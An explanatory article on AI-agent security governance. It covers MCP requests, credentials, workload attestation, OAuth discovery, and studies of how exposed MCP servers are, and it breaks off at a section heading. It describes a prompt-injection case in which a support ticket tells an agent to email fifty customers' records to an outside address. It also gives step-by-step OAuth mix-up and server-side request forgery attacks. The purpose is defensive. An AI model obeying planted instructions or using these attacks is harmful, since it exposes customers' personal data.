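# Security governance of AI agents and machine-to-machine traffic: authentication, API discovery and data-exfiltration controls

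## What changes when an AI agent, and not a fixed program, makes the calls?

An AI agent is software in which a language model chooses and carries out actions, usually by calling tools, to reach a goal. Companies use agents to write code, answer customers and move records between business systems, so the agents need real credentials for those systems. Security governance of agents means deciding and enforcing which systems each agent may reach, on whose behalf, how its calls are recorded, and where the data may go afterwards. Most of its methods come from older work on securing communication between programs. Those methods work less well for agents in a few specific places, which are easier to see after following one call from start to finish.

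### From an API call to a tool call

An API (application programming interface) lets one program request data or actions from another. Each combination of address and operation it offers is an endpoint. An invoicing program that needs a customer's address might send an HTTP request, the same kind of message a browser sends, to the lookup endpoint of a customer database. The request has a first line with the operation and the path, then headers (short labelled lines, one of which usually holds a credential), and often a body with the details. The database checks the credential and that its holder may read customer records, then sends the record back.

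Authentication checks that a caller is who or what it says it is, and authorization determines what an authenticated caller may do. The credential is often an access token, a usually short-lived string that lets its holder use a particular service within stated limits. Scopes set those limits. Each scope is a named permission attached to the token, such as permission to read files. A bearer token is an access token that works for anyone who holds it, including someone who stole it.

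In the invoicing program, a developer decided beforehand when to send the request. In an agent, the surrounding application gives a language model a task and a list of tools. The model writes a tool call, which is a request to run a named tool with given arguments. The application sends the request, then adds the response to the text the model reads before choosing the next step. Because the model has no direct access to the network, there is always conventional software between its choice and the effect of that choice. A rule enforced in that software applies whatever the model writes.

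### The Model Context Protocol

Without a shared standard, developers have to write a separate connector for each pairing of application and system. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), which the AI company Anthropic open-sourced in November 2024, gives AI applications a standard way to find and call outside tools and data sources. MCP's *Architecture overview* divides the work between a host, its clients and the servers. The host is the AI application, which runs one MCP client per connection to send requests. The MCP server is a program that offers tools or data and answers those requests. It is often a thin layer over an existing API, so it receives a tool call and then makes an ordinary API call of its own.

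A client can fetch a server's tool catalogue with a `tools/list` request. The reply gives each tool's name, a plain-language description and a schema of the arguments it takes. The host passes all of this to the model, so whoever writes the server also writes some of the text that steers the agent.

Under the design principles in the Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026), the host keeps the full conversation, and a server should not be able to read all of it or see into other servers. This is good for privacy, but a database's MCP server can't easily judge whether a lookup makes sense, because it receives the request for a record without the message that prompted it.

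An MCP server can be local or remote. A local server runs on the same machine as the host. The client starts it as a subprocess and exchanges messages with it over standard input and output (stdio). *Detecting Shadow AI* (2026), a study of unapproved agents on company computers, cites MCP's documentation, which warns that a local server runs with the permissions of the user's account. Stdio messages do not cross the network, so a network monitor misses them, though it may catch any API calls the local server then makes. A remote server runs elsewhere and typically serves many clients over HTTP.

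### A support agent and its normal day

An imaginary company has a support agent that answers customers' emails. On a normal day it handles 400 tickets. For each ticket it makes five tool calls, to open the ticket, fetch the earlier messages, look up the customer, email a reply and close the ticket. That makes 2,000 tool calls a day, including 400 lookups that each return one customer record. The agent uses four systems and holds a credential for each.

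| System | Connection | Credential | What the credential permits |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ticketing system | Direct API calls | Access token | Reading and closing tickets |
| Customer database | The database's remote MCP server | Access token with the scope `customers:read` | Looking up any customer |
| Email service | Direct API calls | Access token | Sending mail from the support address to anyone |
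| Language model provider | Direct API calls | API key | Sending text to the model and receiving its output |

The permissions are much wider than the day's work requires. The database token covers every customer, including those who did not write in. The email token has to allow any recipient, since a new customer may write from any address. The MCP server also has its own password for the database behind it, a fifth credential that the agent never sees.

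### One request in full

In the 2026-07-28 version of MCP, the lookup for one ticket takes this form. A real request would have the token in place of the words in angle brackets.

```http
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
Host: customers.example.com
Authorization: Bearer <access token>
Content-Type: application/json
Accept: application/json, text/event-stream
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: get_customer
MCP-Protocol-Version: 2026-07-28

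{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 41,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "get_customer",
    "arguments": { "email": "dana@example.org" },
    "_meta": {
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientInfo": {
        "name": "support-agent",
        "version": "3.2"
      },
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/protocolVersion": "2026-07-28",
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientCapabilities": {}
    }
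  }
}
```

| Part | What it does |
|---|---|
| `POST /mcp` | Delivers the message to the server's single MCP address; every message is a new POST |
| `Host` | Names the site the request is for |
| `Authorization` | Carries the access token |
| `Content-Type` | Marks the body as JSON, a text format made of named fields |
| `Accept` | Lists the reply formats the client can read: one JSON object, or a stream of events |
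| `Mcp-Method` | Repeats the body's `method` where network equipment can read it |
| `Mcp-Name` | Repeats the name of the tool |
| `MCP-Protocol-Version` | Gives the version of MCP in use |
| `jsonrpc` | Gives the version of JSON-RPC, the general request-and-reply format under MCP |
| `id` | Pairs the reply with this request |
| `method` | Names the operation, here running a tool |
| `name` and `arguments` under `params` | Name the tool and supply its inputs |
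| `clientInfo` | Gives the client software's name and version; optional |
| `protocolVersion` | Repeats the version inside the body; required |
| `clientCapabilities` | Lists optional features the client supports, such as putting a question to the user; required even when empty |

The sample request in the MCP project's release announcement omits the fields in the last two rows, so a server that follows the specification has to reject it. Developers who copy the sample will need to add both fields.

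The request contains two fields that look like an identity, `clientInfo` and the token, but only the token can serve as one. The client fills in `clientInfo` itself and the protocol does not verify it, so any program can call itself `support-agent`. The Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) advises against relying on `clientInfo` for security decisions. The token can serve as an identity only if the server checks it, using a procedure MCP borrows from the web's OAuth standard. But the Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* makes that procedure optional, so a server can comply with MCP and still answer anyone who reaches it.

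An organisation can route calls through a gateway, a server that checks, limits and logs them. The fields are repeated in the headers because reading a header takes less computation than parsing a body. But a caller could put a harmless tool in `Mcp-Name` and a dangerous one in the body, and the gateway would approve the first while the server ran the second. The Model Context Protocol's *Streamable HTTP* (2026) prevents this by requiring any server that processes the body to compare the two and reject a mismatch. Older versions of MCP have no such rule, and the specification recommends that gateways enforcing policy on these headers reject requests that use those versions.

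Even when the headers are accurate, a gateway that reads only headers can tell that the agent called `get_customer`, but not whose record it fetched. The server's author can also mark simple arguments to be copied into headers. This helps with a value like a region code, but it is a poor idea for an email address, which would then end up in every log along the way.

### The end of sessions

Before July 2026, a client had to send an `initialize` message before it could make this request over HTTP. Under the previous version, 2025-11-25, the server could reply with a session number that the client then had to attach to every later call. One copy of the server often held the session's details in its memory, so all later calls had to reach that copy. Google (2026) described this as a hard wall when it tried to run MCP servers across its cloud, and helped lead the redesign. The new version drops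 the opening exchange and the session number. Each request carries its own version and capabilities, so any copy of the server can answer it.

Some tasks, such as filling a shopping basket, need memory from one call to the next. As the Model Context Protocol (2026) project describes the change, the server creates an explicit identifier, for example a `basket_id`, and returns it to the model as ordinary data. The model then passes it back as an argument in later calls.

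This is mostly a gain for security, because a gateway can now evaluate each request by its contents. However, MCP no longer links an agent's calls together, so anyone who wants to see the support agent's 2,000 calls as a sequence has to reconstruct it from logs. The specification reserves fields for trace identifiers that would help, but does not require clients to fill them in. Old-style traffic will also continue, because clients that support both versions may fall back to the `initialize` exchange when they connect to an older server.

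### Where an agent differs from an ordinary service

A nightly invoicing job reads the same customer database as the support agent, but a developer can list every call the job will ever make. From that list, a security team can derive the exact permissions the job needs, and any call outside the list means a fault or an intrusion. The support agent has no such list. It might look up one customer for most tickets and three for a ticket about a shared household account, although nobody wrote a rule telling it to do so. Its permissions therefore have to cover what it might reasonably need, and an unusual call is only weak evidence of trouble. *Back to the Future*, an August 2026 post from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), warns that agents can try several unpredictable paths to a goal, and that even a tightly limited agent may find a forgotten credential and use it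 to gain more access.

The text an agent reads can also redirect it. Suppose someone opens a ticket that contains, below an ordinary complaint, an instruction to look up fifty other customers and email their records to an outside address. This is prompt injection, in which an attacker plants instructions in material an agent reads so that the agent will follow them. If the agent complies, the result is data exfiltration, the unauthorised movement of data out of an organisation. The requests are genuine. The tokens are valid, the scopes allow the lookups, and the email service sends mail as it should.

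Security engineers call a program in this position a confused deputy, meaning that an outsider can trick it into using its authority on the outsider's behalf. The problem is old and usually fixable. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C argues that language models are different. In SQL injection, an attacker types database commands into a web form, and a parameterised query prevents this by treating whatever is typed as data. A language model has no such separation, because it receives instructions and data as one run of text and predicts what comes next. Training it to favour some parts of the text over others lowers the odds of an attack but doesn't rule one out. David C concludes that designers should plan for the worst case, in which the attacker has direct use of the agent's tools. For the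 support agent, that would give anyone who can open a ticket access to the whole customer database and the company's outgoing mail.

Many agents also use a person's account, whereas the invoicing job has its own, called a machine identity. NIST reports that giving an agent one's own credentials has quickly become common, and that a locally deployed agent running under its user's account can impersonate that user and act with broad access. If the support agent ran on a team leader's login, it could open everything the team leader can, and if it closed 400 tickets, the ticketing system would record the team leader as having closed them.

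Agents are also quick to set up. The invoicing job probably went through a budget, a review and a release. An employee can have an agent running in minutes by adding a server to a configuration file and pasting in a key, and NIST observes that a long-lived API key is often the fastest way to get started. The agent may run for only an afternoon, while the key stays valid for years. The tools agents use are also getting easier to build. A UK AI Security Institute study, *How are AI agents used?* (Stein, 2026), detected AI assistance in 62% of the new public MCP servers created in February 2026, up from 6% in January 2025.

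### What stays the same

Existing gateways, rate limits, token services and logs work on an agent's traffic. The lookup request above is an HTTP message with a bearer token, and the agent's calls to the ticketing and email systems do not use MCP. A server that receives this traffic cannot tell for sure whether a model or a script wrote it. NIST treats shared credentials, static keys and over-broad access as decades-old identity management problems, and existing standards as the place to start. Some commenters on the post objected that permissions control what an agent can access but not what it does with that access.

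AI agents bring both old and new security problems. Borrowed logins, hasty deployment and excess permissions long predate agents, and the known remedies still apply, though neglecting them does more harm when agents are involved. It is harder to secure a sequence of calls that is not fixed in advance, because this weakens any remedy that depends on knowing what normal behaviour looks like. The new problem is that text can redirect an agent, so even one that is correctly identified and authorised can do an attacker's work.

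### How much of this traffic there is

In July 2026 the Model Context Protocol (MCP) project counted close to half a billion monthly downloads of its main software development kits (SDKs), the libraries developers use to build clients and servers. On the same day, Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) put the figure at over 400 million, a fourfold rise since the start of the year. By November the Python and TypeScript SDKs alone had reached about 656 million downloads in 30 days, according to *The Complete Guide to Model Context Protocol (MCP)*, an online tracker that also counted 64,935 servers in the registry.

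Download counts show that developers' interest is large and growing fast, but they don't measure how many agents are running, what those agents are allowed to access, or whether anyone is monitoring them. Automated build systems may fetch the same library every time they test a program, so one project can account for thousands of downloads. A single download can also serve an agent that makes a million calls.

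Stein provides more direct evidence by looking at what the tools do. The study classified 177,436 public tools and weighted them by downloads where possible, for 3,854 servers. The download-weighted share of "action" tools, which change something outside the agent, rose from 27% in November 2024 to 65% in February 2026, largely because of general-purpose tools that operate a browser or a whole computer. Software development accounted for 90% of server downloads, so a customer support agent is not the typical case. Stein could not observe whether anyone called the tools after downloading them, and the data exclude private servers like the one in front of the support company's database.

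Counts of actual calls are scarce, but Honeycomb, which sells software for monitoring other software, has published one. Its director of AI strategy reported in the July release announcement that agents now make nearly 20% of all monthly interactive queries on its service.

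## How can an agent prove which agent it is?

When the support agent looks up a customer, the database's MCP server must rely mostly on the credential attached to the request to identify the agent, because `clientInfo` is unverified and the network address shows at most which machine or gateway sent the message. Credentials vary a lot in how much they prove. The simplest are fixed strings that work like passwords, while the most elaborate come from a local program that inspects a process before issuing it a credential. This difference matters most after someone has copied the credential.

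### API keys and bearer tokens

A static API key is a long random string that a service creates once and accepts until someone cancels it. The service looks up the key to find the account it belongs to. If the support agent, a test script and a former contractor all hold the same key, the service cannot tell them apart.

A thief who copies an API key can usually use it from anywhere. METR (2026), a nonprofit that evaluates AI models, disclosed that attackers stole one of its API keys in March 2026 and used it to run publicly available models. Woollacott (2026) reported in *Hackers ran up a $600,000 AI bill after swiping API keys* that they used $600,000 worth of credits and that nobody noticed for weeks. METR was not paying for the credits, and it believes the thieves reached no sensitive information. The support agent has the same type of key for its model provider, but the company would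 probably have to pay for anything a thief used.

API keys also tend to end up in files. According to Trail of Bits' *Insecure credential storage plagues MCP* (2025), most MCP servers take their credentials from command-line arguments or environment variables (settings the operating system passes to a program), and these often come from a configuration file the AI application manages. If the application stores that file insecurely, other programs on the machine can read the key. Large vendors also accept API keys. Okta's *The Secrets Agentic AI Leaves Behind* reports that three in four plugins for Microsoft's Security Copilot can use one. An administrator creates a long-lived key and uploads it to Microsoft, and Copilot sends it with every request to the protected system.

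An access token is safer mainly because it expires. The authorization server checks the client and then issues a signed token with an expiry time, a list of scopes and usually an audience (the service the token is for). With an ordinary bearer token, the customer database can verify that the authorization server recently approved some client to read customer records, but not that the sender is that client. Someone who copies the token at 10:05 can therefore read customer records until it expires at, say, 11:00.

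The client must also authenticate to the authorization server to get its tokens. If it uses a static secret, anyone who copies the secret can keep requesting new tokens, so the tokens' short expiry time provides very little protection.

### Tokens bound to a private key

The authorization server can tie a token to a key pair so that someone who steals only the token cannot use it. The client signs with a private key that it never sends, and anyone with the matching public key can check the signature. DPoP (Demonstrating Proof of Possession) and mutual TLS are the two main ways to do this.

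With DPoP, the token contains a fingerprint of the client's public key. The client attaches to each request a signed proof containing the HTTP method, the URL, the time, a unique number and a fingerprint of the token. The database accepts the request only if the signature matches the key identified in the token.

DPoP is slightly awkward to use with MCP. Every MCP message over HTTP is a POST to the same address, so a proof made for one customer lookup would also fit any other tool call. An attacker who captured the token and a fresh proof could attach both to a different request. The server can limit this by rejecting any proof whose unique number it has already seen. Local MCP servers use stdio, so they have no HTTP headers to put a proof in. *JSON Web Token (JWT) Profile for OAuth 2.0 Enveloped Proof of Possession* (Ambekar, 2026) proposes packing the token and the proof into one envelope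 that would also work outside HTTP, and names MCP as a use. It is an individual's draft and has not been adopted as a standard.

Mutual TLS works at the level of the connection. In ordinary TLS, the encryption under HTTPS, normally only the server presents a certificate. In mutual TLS, the client also presents one and proves that it holds the matching private key. The token contains a fingerprint of the client's certificate, so the database can reject a token that arrives over a connection made with a different certificate. This is harder behind a gateway, which ends the agent's connection and opens its own. The database then receives the gateway's certificate and has to rely on the gateway to pass on the agent's details.

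| Credential | What the service can establish | What a thief gains from a copy |
|---|---|---|
| Static API key | The caller has the key for a certain account | The account's access, until someone cancels the key |
| Bearer token | An authorization server recently approved some client for these scopes | The same access, until the token expires |
| Token bound to a key (DPoP or mutual TLS) | The caller also holds the private key of the client that received the token | Almost nothing from the token alone; access until expiry if the private key leaks too |
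| Workload identity after attestation | The key belongs to a process with known properties on a known machine | Nothing from the certificate alone; with its private key, the use of that identity until the certificate expires |

The last two rows work best together. Key binding shows that the sender holds a certain private key, but not how the support agent got that key. A developer might have pasted it into a file. Attestation addresses this by checking evidence about a machine or program before giving it an identity.

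### SPIFFE and SPIRE, step by step

SPIFFE (Secure Production Identity Framework for Everyone) is an open standard for naming pieces of running software, which it calls workloads, and for proving those names. SPIRE is a program that implements the standard. A SPIFFE ID looks like a web address. As KubeDojo's *Module 4.8* explains, it starts with a trust domain, the part of an organisation that shares one signing authority, followed by a path the organisation chooses.

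Suppose the support agent runs in Kubernetes, a system for starting and managing packaged programs, on machines rented from Amazon. An engineer first registers its name together with the properties a process must have to receive it:

```text
SPIFFE ID   spiffe://prod.example.com/ns/support/sa/support-agent
Selectors   k8s:ns:support
            k8s:sa:support-agent
            k8s:container-image:<image name and hash>
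```

Here `ns` is a namespace, a section of the cluster, and `sa` is the service account that Kubernetes runs the program under. The hash is a fingerprint of the packaged program that changes if anyone alters the package. According to SPIFFE's *SPIRE Concepts*, every machine runs a small helper program called the SPIRE Agent, which has nothing to do with AI.

1. In node attestation, the helper proves which machine it is on. It obtains an identity document from Amazon and passes it to the central SPIRE server, which asks Amazon whether the document is valid. The server then gives the helper an identity of its own.
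2. The helper downloads the registration entries for its machine and requests a signed identity document for each. The server signs these documents, called SVIDs (SPIFFE Verifiable Identity Documents), and the helper stores them in memory.
3. In workload attestation, the support agent asks the helper for an identity through a local connection. The helper gets the caller's process number from the operating system, looks up its namespace, service account and image, and compares them with the registered properties. If they match, it hands over the SVID and its private key.
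4. The helper replaces each SVID before it runs out. Encryption Consulting gives the default lifetime as one hour for SVIDs in certificate form.

The support agent's certificate would contain roughly this:

```text
Name         spiffe://prod.example.com/ns/support/sa/support-agent
Public key   <matches the private key the agent holds>
Valid from   2026-12-05 09:00
Valid until  2026-12-05 10:00
Signed by    SPIRE server for prod.example.com
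```

The agent needs no starting password, so a thief can't find one in a configuration file. The agent can present the certificate over mutual TLS, or use it to authenticate to an authorization server and get an access token. SVIDs also come as tokens, which are convenient where a gateway sits in the path, but these are bearer tokens, so a thief can reuse a stolen one until it expires.

SPIFFE names a caller but doesn't grant it any permissions, so the customer database still needs its own rule allowing that name to read customer records. The name is also useful only with services that trust the company's SPIRE server. The company can set up that trust for its own database, but an outside email service or model provider may accept only its own keys and tokens.

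How much attestation proves depends on which properties the engineer chose to check. Palo Alto Networks lists the service account, the hash of the program file and the image identifier among the options. A service account shows only how the program was started, so any code running under the account gets the name. A file hash is stronger, but many agents are Python scripts, and the hash may then identify the Python interpreter rather than the script. The image hash covers both the interpreter and the script. None of these checks helps much if an attacker controls the operating system, because the helper gets its evidence from there.

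### What should the identity name?

The certificate above identifies a program and its operator, but it has no fields for the model, prompt, tools or ticket. Whether it should include them is an open question, even at NIST. In *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026) asked the public which metadata an agent's identity needs, and whether that metadata should be fixed or change with each task. They list SPIFFE and SPIRE as one way to identify agents.

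Suppose two copies of the support agent share the day's 400 tickets. Both match the same registration entry, so both receive the same SPIFFE ID. If they run on a single machine, they also receive the same certificate and private key from the helper's memory. The shared ID is convenient for permissions, because the copies do the same job and need the same access. But if one copy reads a malicious ticket and starts looking up strangers, the security team would want to cut off only that copy, and the shared ID does not allow that.

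A model swap causes the opposite problem, because the agent changes but its name stays the same. The support agent calls its model over the internet, and the provider may put a new version behind the same model name. Nothing changes on the company's machines, so the image hash still matches and the helper issues the usual certificate, even though the new model might be easier to trick or might use tools differently. Putting the model version in the identity would force someone to approve each upgrade, which seems sensible for an agent that moves money but tiresome for one that sorts tickets. Either way, the company has to trust the provider to report which model is answering.

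The prompt and tool set are even harder to identify. A company can hash its standard instructions, but tool descriptions arrive from MCP servers while the agent runs, and each ticket adds new text. A hash of everything the model reads would change at every step, so nobody could write a permission rule for it in advance.

An agent can also start sub-agents to do parts of a job. Suppose the support agent starts one to summarise a long email thread, and it finishes in ten seconds. If the sub-agent runs as a separate process, SPIRE can give it a name, but a one-hour certificate would last 360 times as long as the job. If it is just another conversation with the model inside the same program, there is no new process for the helper to inspect. The sub-agent is then visible only within the application, so other services have to rely on what the application reports about it.

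One name probably can't hold all of this information. Permissions need a name that stays the same for months, so it can identify the operator and the job, as in the SPIFFE ID above. The copy's number, the model version and a hash of the standard instructions work better as separate fields, which services can log and a strict policy can check. The task belongs in a short-lived access token that expires when the ticket closes. Each field also needs a source that can attest to it. The SPIRE server can do this for the image, but usually only the application can do it for the prompt.

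Splitting identity up this way creates a risk that a service will check that each piece is genuine but not that the pieces belong together. Okutomi (2026), in *A Core Acceptance Profile for Session-Bound Agent Identity*, uses the term "context diversion" for cases where a service accepts a valid credential for an agent, task or customer organisation other than the one it was meant for. To prevent this, the draft requires the service to check the grant of authority, the private key and the current connection together before it accepts the agent.

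Attestation can show that the approved image is running on an approved machine, but even a perfect description of the software would not predict what the model will do. A planted instruction can still redirect the agent. Attestation does rule out some other explanations for a suspicious lookup, such as an impostor program or an altered image.

### Agents on other organisations' websites

The support agent sometimes has to visit a site that its company doesn't run, such as a courier's tracking page when a parcel is missing. The courier hasn't issued the agent a credential and has no reason to trust the company's SPIRE server. Websites have traditionally recognised automated visitors by the User-Agent header, which anyone can fake, or by network address. Addresses change, and unrelated customers of a cloud provider may share them.

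Web Bot Auth replaces these clues with signed HTTP requests. The agent's operator publishes its public keys at a standard address on its own domain. The agent signs each request and adds headers that point to those keys, list the parts of the request the signature covers, and give an expiry time. The courier's site fetches the public key and checks the signature. It can then tell that a holder of `example.com`'s key sent the request, and apply any rule it has for that company.

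This helps a site tell a known company's agent from an impostor, but a valid signature is no evidence of good intentions, since anyone can register a domain and publish a key. The site also learns nothing about the customer whose parcel is missing unless the operator includes that information. A signature covers only the parts of the request it lists. If it covers the site's name but not the page, someone who intercepts it may be able to reuse it on another page of the same site until it expires.

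The Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which writes many of the internet's technical standards, set up a working group on Web Bot Auth in 2025. Its WIMSE group (Workload Identity in Multi-System Environments), formed in 2024, works on a related problem. When a request passes through several services, possibly in different clouds, each service needs to know which workload called it. In WIMSE's design, a workload presents a signed token containing its name and public key, then proves with each request that it holds the private key. The name can be a SPIFFE ID, so WIMSE builds on SPIFFE.

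Proposals specifically for AI agents are at an earlier stage. *AAuth-Bootstrap* (2026), a self-described exploratory proposal, uses names of the form `aauth:local@domain`, each tied to a signing key that the domain publishes. Okutomi's and Ambekar's drafts are individual submissions, which anyone can post, and they expire after six months unless the author renews them. A company that builds on one of them now may have to rebuild later. NIST's planned project won't soon settle how agents should prove their identity either, because Booth and colleagues leave external agents from untrusted sources out of its first phase.

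### What agents and MCP servers use in practice

Articles about MCP security often repeat that only 8.5% of MCP servers use OAuth, the web standard for issuing access tokens. The number comes from *State of MCP Server Security 2025* (Skverer, 2025), which the security company Astrix published on 15 October 2025. The report used a language model to classify the credentials mentioned in the README files (introductory documentation) of 5,205 GitHub repositories. About 53% relied on static API keys or personal access tokens and 8.5% on OAuth. Another 26.4% mentioned credentials that the model could not classify.

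This evidence is weaker than the headline suggests. The researchers ran none of the servers, and about 30% of the repositories did not contain a real MCP server, so the percentages may describe fewer than 4,000 servers. The study also counted the credentials a server uses to reach the service behind it, which don't show how clients log in to the server. The support company's database server would count as static in this study because it reaches the database with a password, even though the agent presents an access token to the server.

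People tend to omit the caveats when they repeat the number. Dumbris (2026), in *Only 8.5% of MCP Servers Use OAuth*, says the data came partly from "actual runtime behavior" and covered enterprise deployments, but Skverer's study involved neither.

Zhou, Zhang and colleagues (2026) provide the best evidence on client logins in *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers*. They used internet search engines for devices and services to find 28,715 possible addresses, sent each an MCP greeting, and confirmed 7,973 live remote servers. Of these, 40.55% exposed their tools without authentication, 30.45% used OAuth, and 29% used a static token or API key. OAuth was therefore far more common for client logins than the 8.5% figure implies, though less common than no authentication.

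Most of the open servers that Zhou and colleagues examined at random were tests or demonstrations without sensitive data. One was a customer database much like the support company's. Its owner had meant it for internal use and left out authentication by mistake, so anyone who could connect could query over 5,000 records with names, email addresses, phone numbers and physical addresses. The overall share of open servers could be somewhat too high, because a well-protected server may reject unknown clients before a scanner can identify it, and the scan does not cover servers on private networks.

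*Exposed by Design* (Padilla, 2026) has newer but narrower data. In July 2026, Padilla confirmed 640 servers on the public internet and tested 414 of them. Of those tested, 380 (91.8%) had no OAuth. The remaining 8.2% is close to the older figure of 8.5% only by coincidence, because Padilla looked at client logins. Some of those 380 servers may still have restricted access by other means, such as an API key. The sample may also lean towards open servers, which are easier to test from outside. The set of servers changed quickly too, and 41.6% of those found in one scan were gone three days later.

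Whether a remote MCP server requires authentication may depend more on its hosting platform than on its developer's choices. Sohail (2026), in *Characterizing Network Centralization and Observability in the Remote MCP Ecosystem*, reached 76 remote servers, using data from June 2025. On Smithery, a commercial host that puts a login in front of its customers' servers, 53 of 56 required authentication, compared with 10 of 20 elsewhere. The sample is small, and careful developers may prefer Smithery, but a plausible explanation is that Smithery's default protects servers without any work from their authors.

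All four studies cover servers, so they don't show how many agents have an attested identity or a key-bound token. The studies of public servers also provide little evidence about the private ones where companies keep customer data.

### NIST's token-protection guidelines

On 15 September 2026 NIST and the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) finalised Interagency Report 8587 on protecting tokens from theft and forgery. It is voluntary and mainly for federal agencies and their cloud providers. Forgery is more dangerous than token theft because someone who steals the key that signs tokens can make new ones at will. In one of the attacks that prompted the report, intruders forged tokens with a stolen key and took more than 60,000 emails from one agency.

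*CISA and NIST Issue Guidance to Protect Cloud Identity Tokens* (Mascellino, 2026) summarises the requirements for tokens and signing keys. Access tokens should last no more than an hour, and services must reject expired ones. Every token must name its audience, and services must refuse any that don't. Organisations should replace signing keys at least every 90 days in high-impact systems and at least once a year in others. Moderate- and high-impact systems must keep signing keys in hardware-backed or isolated storage. Tokens must never appear in logs.

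Under the audience rule, the support agent's token for the customer database would not work at the email service. A developer can easily break the logging rule by accident, because recording an agent's full requests for debugging also records the `Authorization` header. The one-hour limit caps the damage from a stolen token, but at one lookup a second, a thief could still copy 3,600 customer records in that time.

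The December 2025 draft of *Protecting Tokens and Assertions from Forgery, Theft, and Misuse* (Galluzzo and Regenscheid, 2025) dealt with this more directly, noting that software often cannot log in again the way a person can. For such software, it recommended checking whether the request comes from a registered device and an approved network, whether it fits expected behaviour, and possibly whether the caller holds a private key. Expected behaviour is the difficult check for an agent, because its calls vary from ticket to ticket.

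The final report covers the signed tokens that AI agents use but leaves out the wider risks of agents' access, for which NIST and CISA are still writing guidelines. *NIST and CISA finalize playbook to stop token theft and forgery* (Pogorelec, 2026) explains that the report's main scope is also limited to tokens signed with a private key. Static API keys are outside that scope, so the support company could follow the report fully for its customer database and still keep a years-old key for its model provider in a configuration file.

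## How does an MCP server decide whether to accept a client?

A protected MCP server accepts a client that presents a valid access token issued for that server. The client gets this token through OAuth, which lets a person give an application limited access to a service without sharing a password. In OAuth's terms, the support agent's application is the client, and the customer database's MCP server is a resource server, which checks tokens. The company's authorization server signs people in, asks for their consent and issues the tokens.

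The client and the server may have had no earlier contact, so much of the procedure consists of finding out which authorization server the client should ask for access. Suppose an administrator is connecting the support agent to the customer database for the first time, and the agent has only the address `https://customers.example.com/mcp`.

### From the first refusal to the first lookup

The agent sends its lookup without a token, and the server turns it down:

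```http
HTTP/1.1 401 Unauthorized
WWW-Authenticate: Bearer scope="customers:read",
  resource_metadata="https://customers.example.com/.well-known/oauth-protected-resource/mcp"
```

The `scope` value names the permission this request needs. Without it, the client would request every scope the server advertises, and anyone who later stole the token would get all of them.

The second value is the address of the server's protected resource metadata, a short public document:

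```json
{
  "resource": "https://customers.example.com/mcp",
  "authorization_servers": ["https://auth.example.com"],
  "scopes_supported": ["customers:read"]
}
```

Dissanayaka (2026), in *The Anatomy of MCP Authorization*, explains that the client reads the authorization server's address from the document that the MCP server publishes so that it never has to guess the address and can't be tricked into using the wrong one. However, a malicious MCP server could list an address inside the company's network, such as the one where a cloud machine gets its own credentials, and the client would fetch it. This attack is called server-side request forgery, and clients that run on servers have to guard against it, for example by refusing private network addresses.

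Next the client fetches the authorization server's metadata, which lists the server's login and token addresses and its issuer, the name it signs tokens with. The Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Server Discovery* (2026) requires the issuer to be identical to the address the client used to find the document. A document at `attacker.example` that gives `honest.example` as its issuer fails this test, so an attacker can't use another server's name. The client saves the issuer for a later check.

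The client also needs an ID. The support agent's ID is the web address of a small file that describes the agent and gives the return address where the authorization server may send replies. The authorization server fetches the file and checks that this return address matches the one in the request. This stops an impostor from using the agent's ID to have replies sent to the impostor's own site.

The client then opens the administrator's browser at this address (a real one would encode the punctuation):

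```text
https://auth.example.com/authorize
  ?response_type=code
  &client_id=https://support.example.com/oauth/client.json
  &redirect_uri=https://support.example.com/callback
  &scope=customers:read
  &resource=https://customers.example.com/mcp
  &code_challenge=<hash of a secret>
  &code_challenge_method=S256
  &state=<random value>
```

The authorization server will not send the token itself through the browser. It sends a one-time authorization code, which the client exchanges for a token over a direct connection. Someone might still copy the code on its way, and PKCE (Proof Key for Code Exchange) makes the copy useless. The client invents a random secret, the verifier, and puts only its hash in the browser request:

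`code_challenge = BASE64URL(SHA-256(code_verifier))`

The client reveals the verifier when it exchanges the code, and the authorization server hashes the verifier and compares the result with the hash the client sent earlier. A thief who has the code and the hash can't recover the verifier from the hash. The client must refuse to continue if the authorization server's metadata doesn't list support for PKCE.

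The `resource` parameter names the MCP server the token is for, which prevents other servers from reusing the token. The `state` value must come back unchanged, so an attacker can't insert a reply from a different login into the administrator's browser. The specification recommends `state` but does not require it.

The administrator now signs in and sees a consent page with the client's name and the host name of its return address, so an unknown client can't get access unnoticed. After approval, the authorization server sends the browser back only to a return address that exactly matches one in the client's file, so an attacker can't divert the code to another site. Dissanayaka points out that OAuth collects this consent only once. The agent may make hundreds of later calls that the administrator didn't foresee.

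### The issuer check

One more attack is possible before the client exchanges the code. Suppose the agent's application also connects to a courier's MCP server, and an attacker controls the courier's authorization server.

1. The administrator starts connecting to the courier, and the client opens the attacker's login page.
2. The attacker forwards the browser to the company's own authorization server, using the support agent's ID and code challenge but requesting `customers:read`.
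3. The administrator approves, perhaps out of habit, and the company's server sends a code to the agent.
4. The client believes the code came from the courier's server, so it sends the code there along with the verifier. The attacker exchanges both for a token to the customer database.

This is a mix-up attack. According to the Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices*, PKCE doesn't prevent it because the client itself gives the attacker the verifier, and the `resource` parameter doesn't either because the attacker can rewrite the request before passing it on.

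The July 2026 version adds a check for this. The company's authorization server includes `iss=https://auth.example.com` in its reply, and the client compares that value with the issuer it saved. The saved issuer is the courier's, so the client discards the code. The two values must match exactly, including capitals and slashes. The client must also reject a reply that lacks an `iss` value if the server's metadata indicates that it will include one.

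The Model Context Protocol specification requires clients to check an `iss` value when they receive one, but only recommends that authorization servers send it. If a company's authorization server omits the value and the attacker's metadata doesn't indicate that one will be sent, the client proceeds and the attack works. Some summaries overstate this protection. *Breaking MCP at the Identity Layer*, published by SlashID, which sells identity monitoring, lists issuer validation as mandatory. According to the specification, a later version is expected to make sending the value compulsory, so a company choosing an authorization server now has good reason to require it.

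### The token and the call

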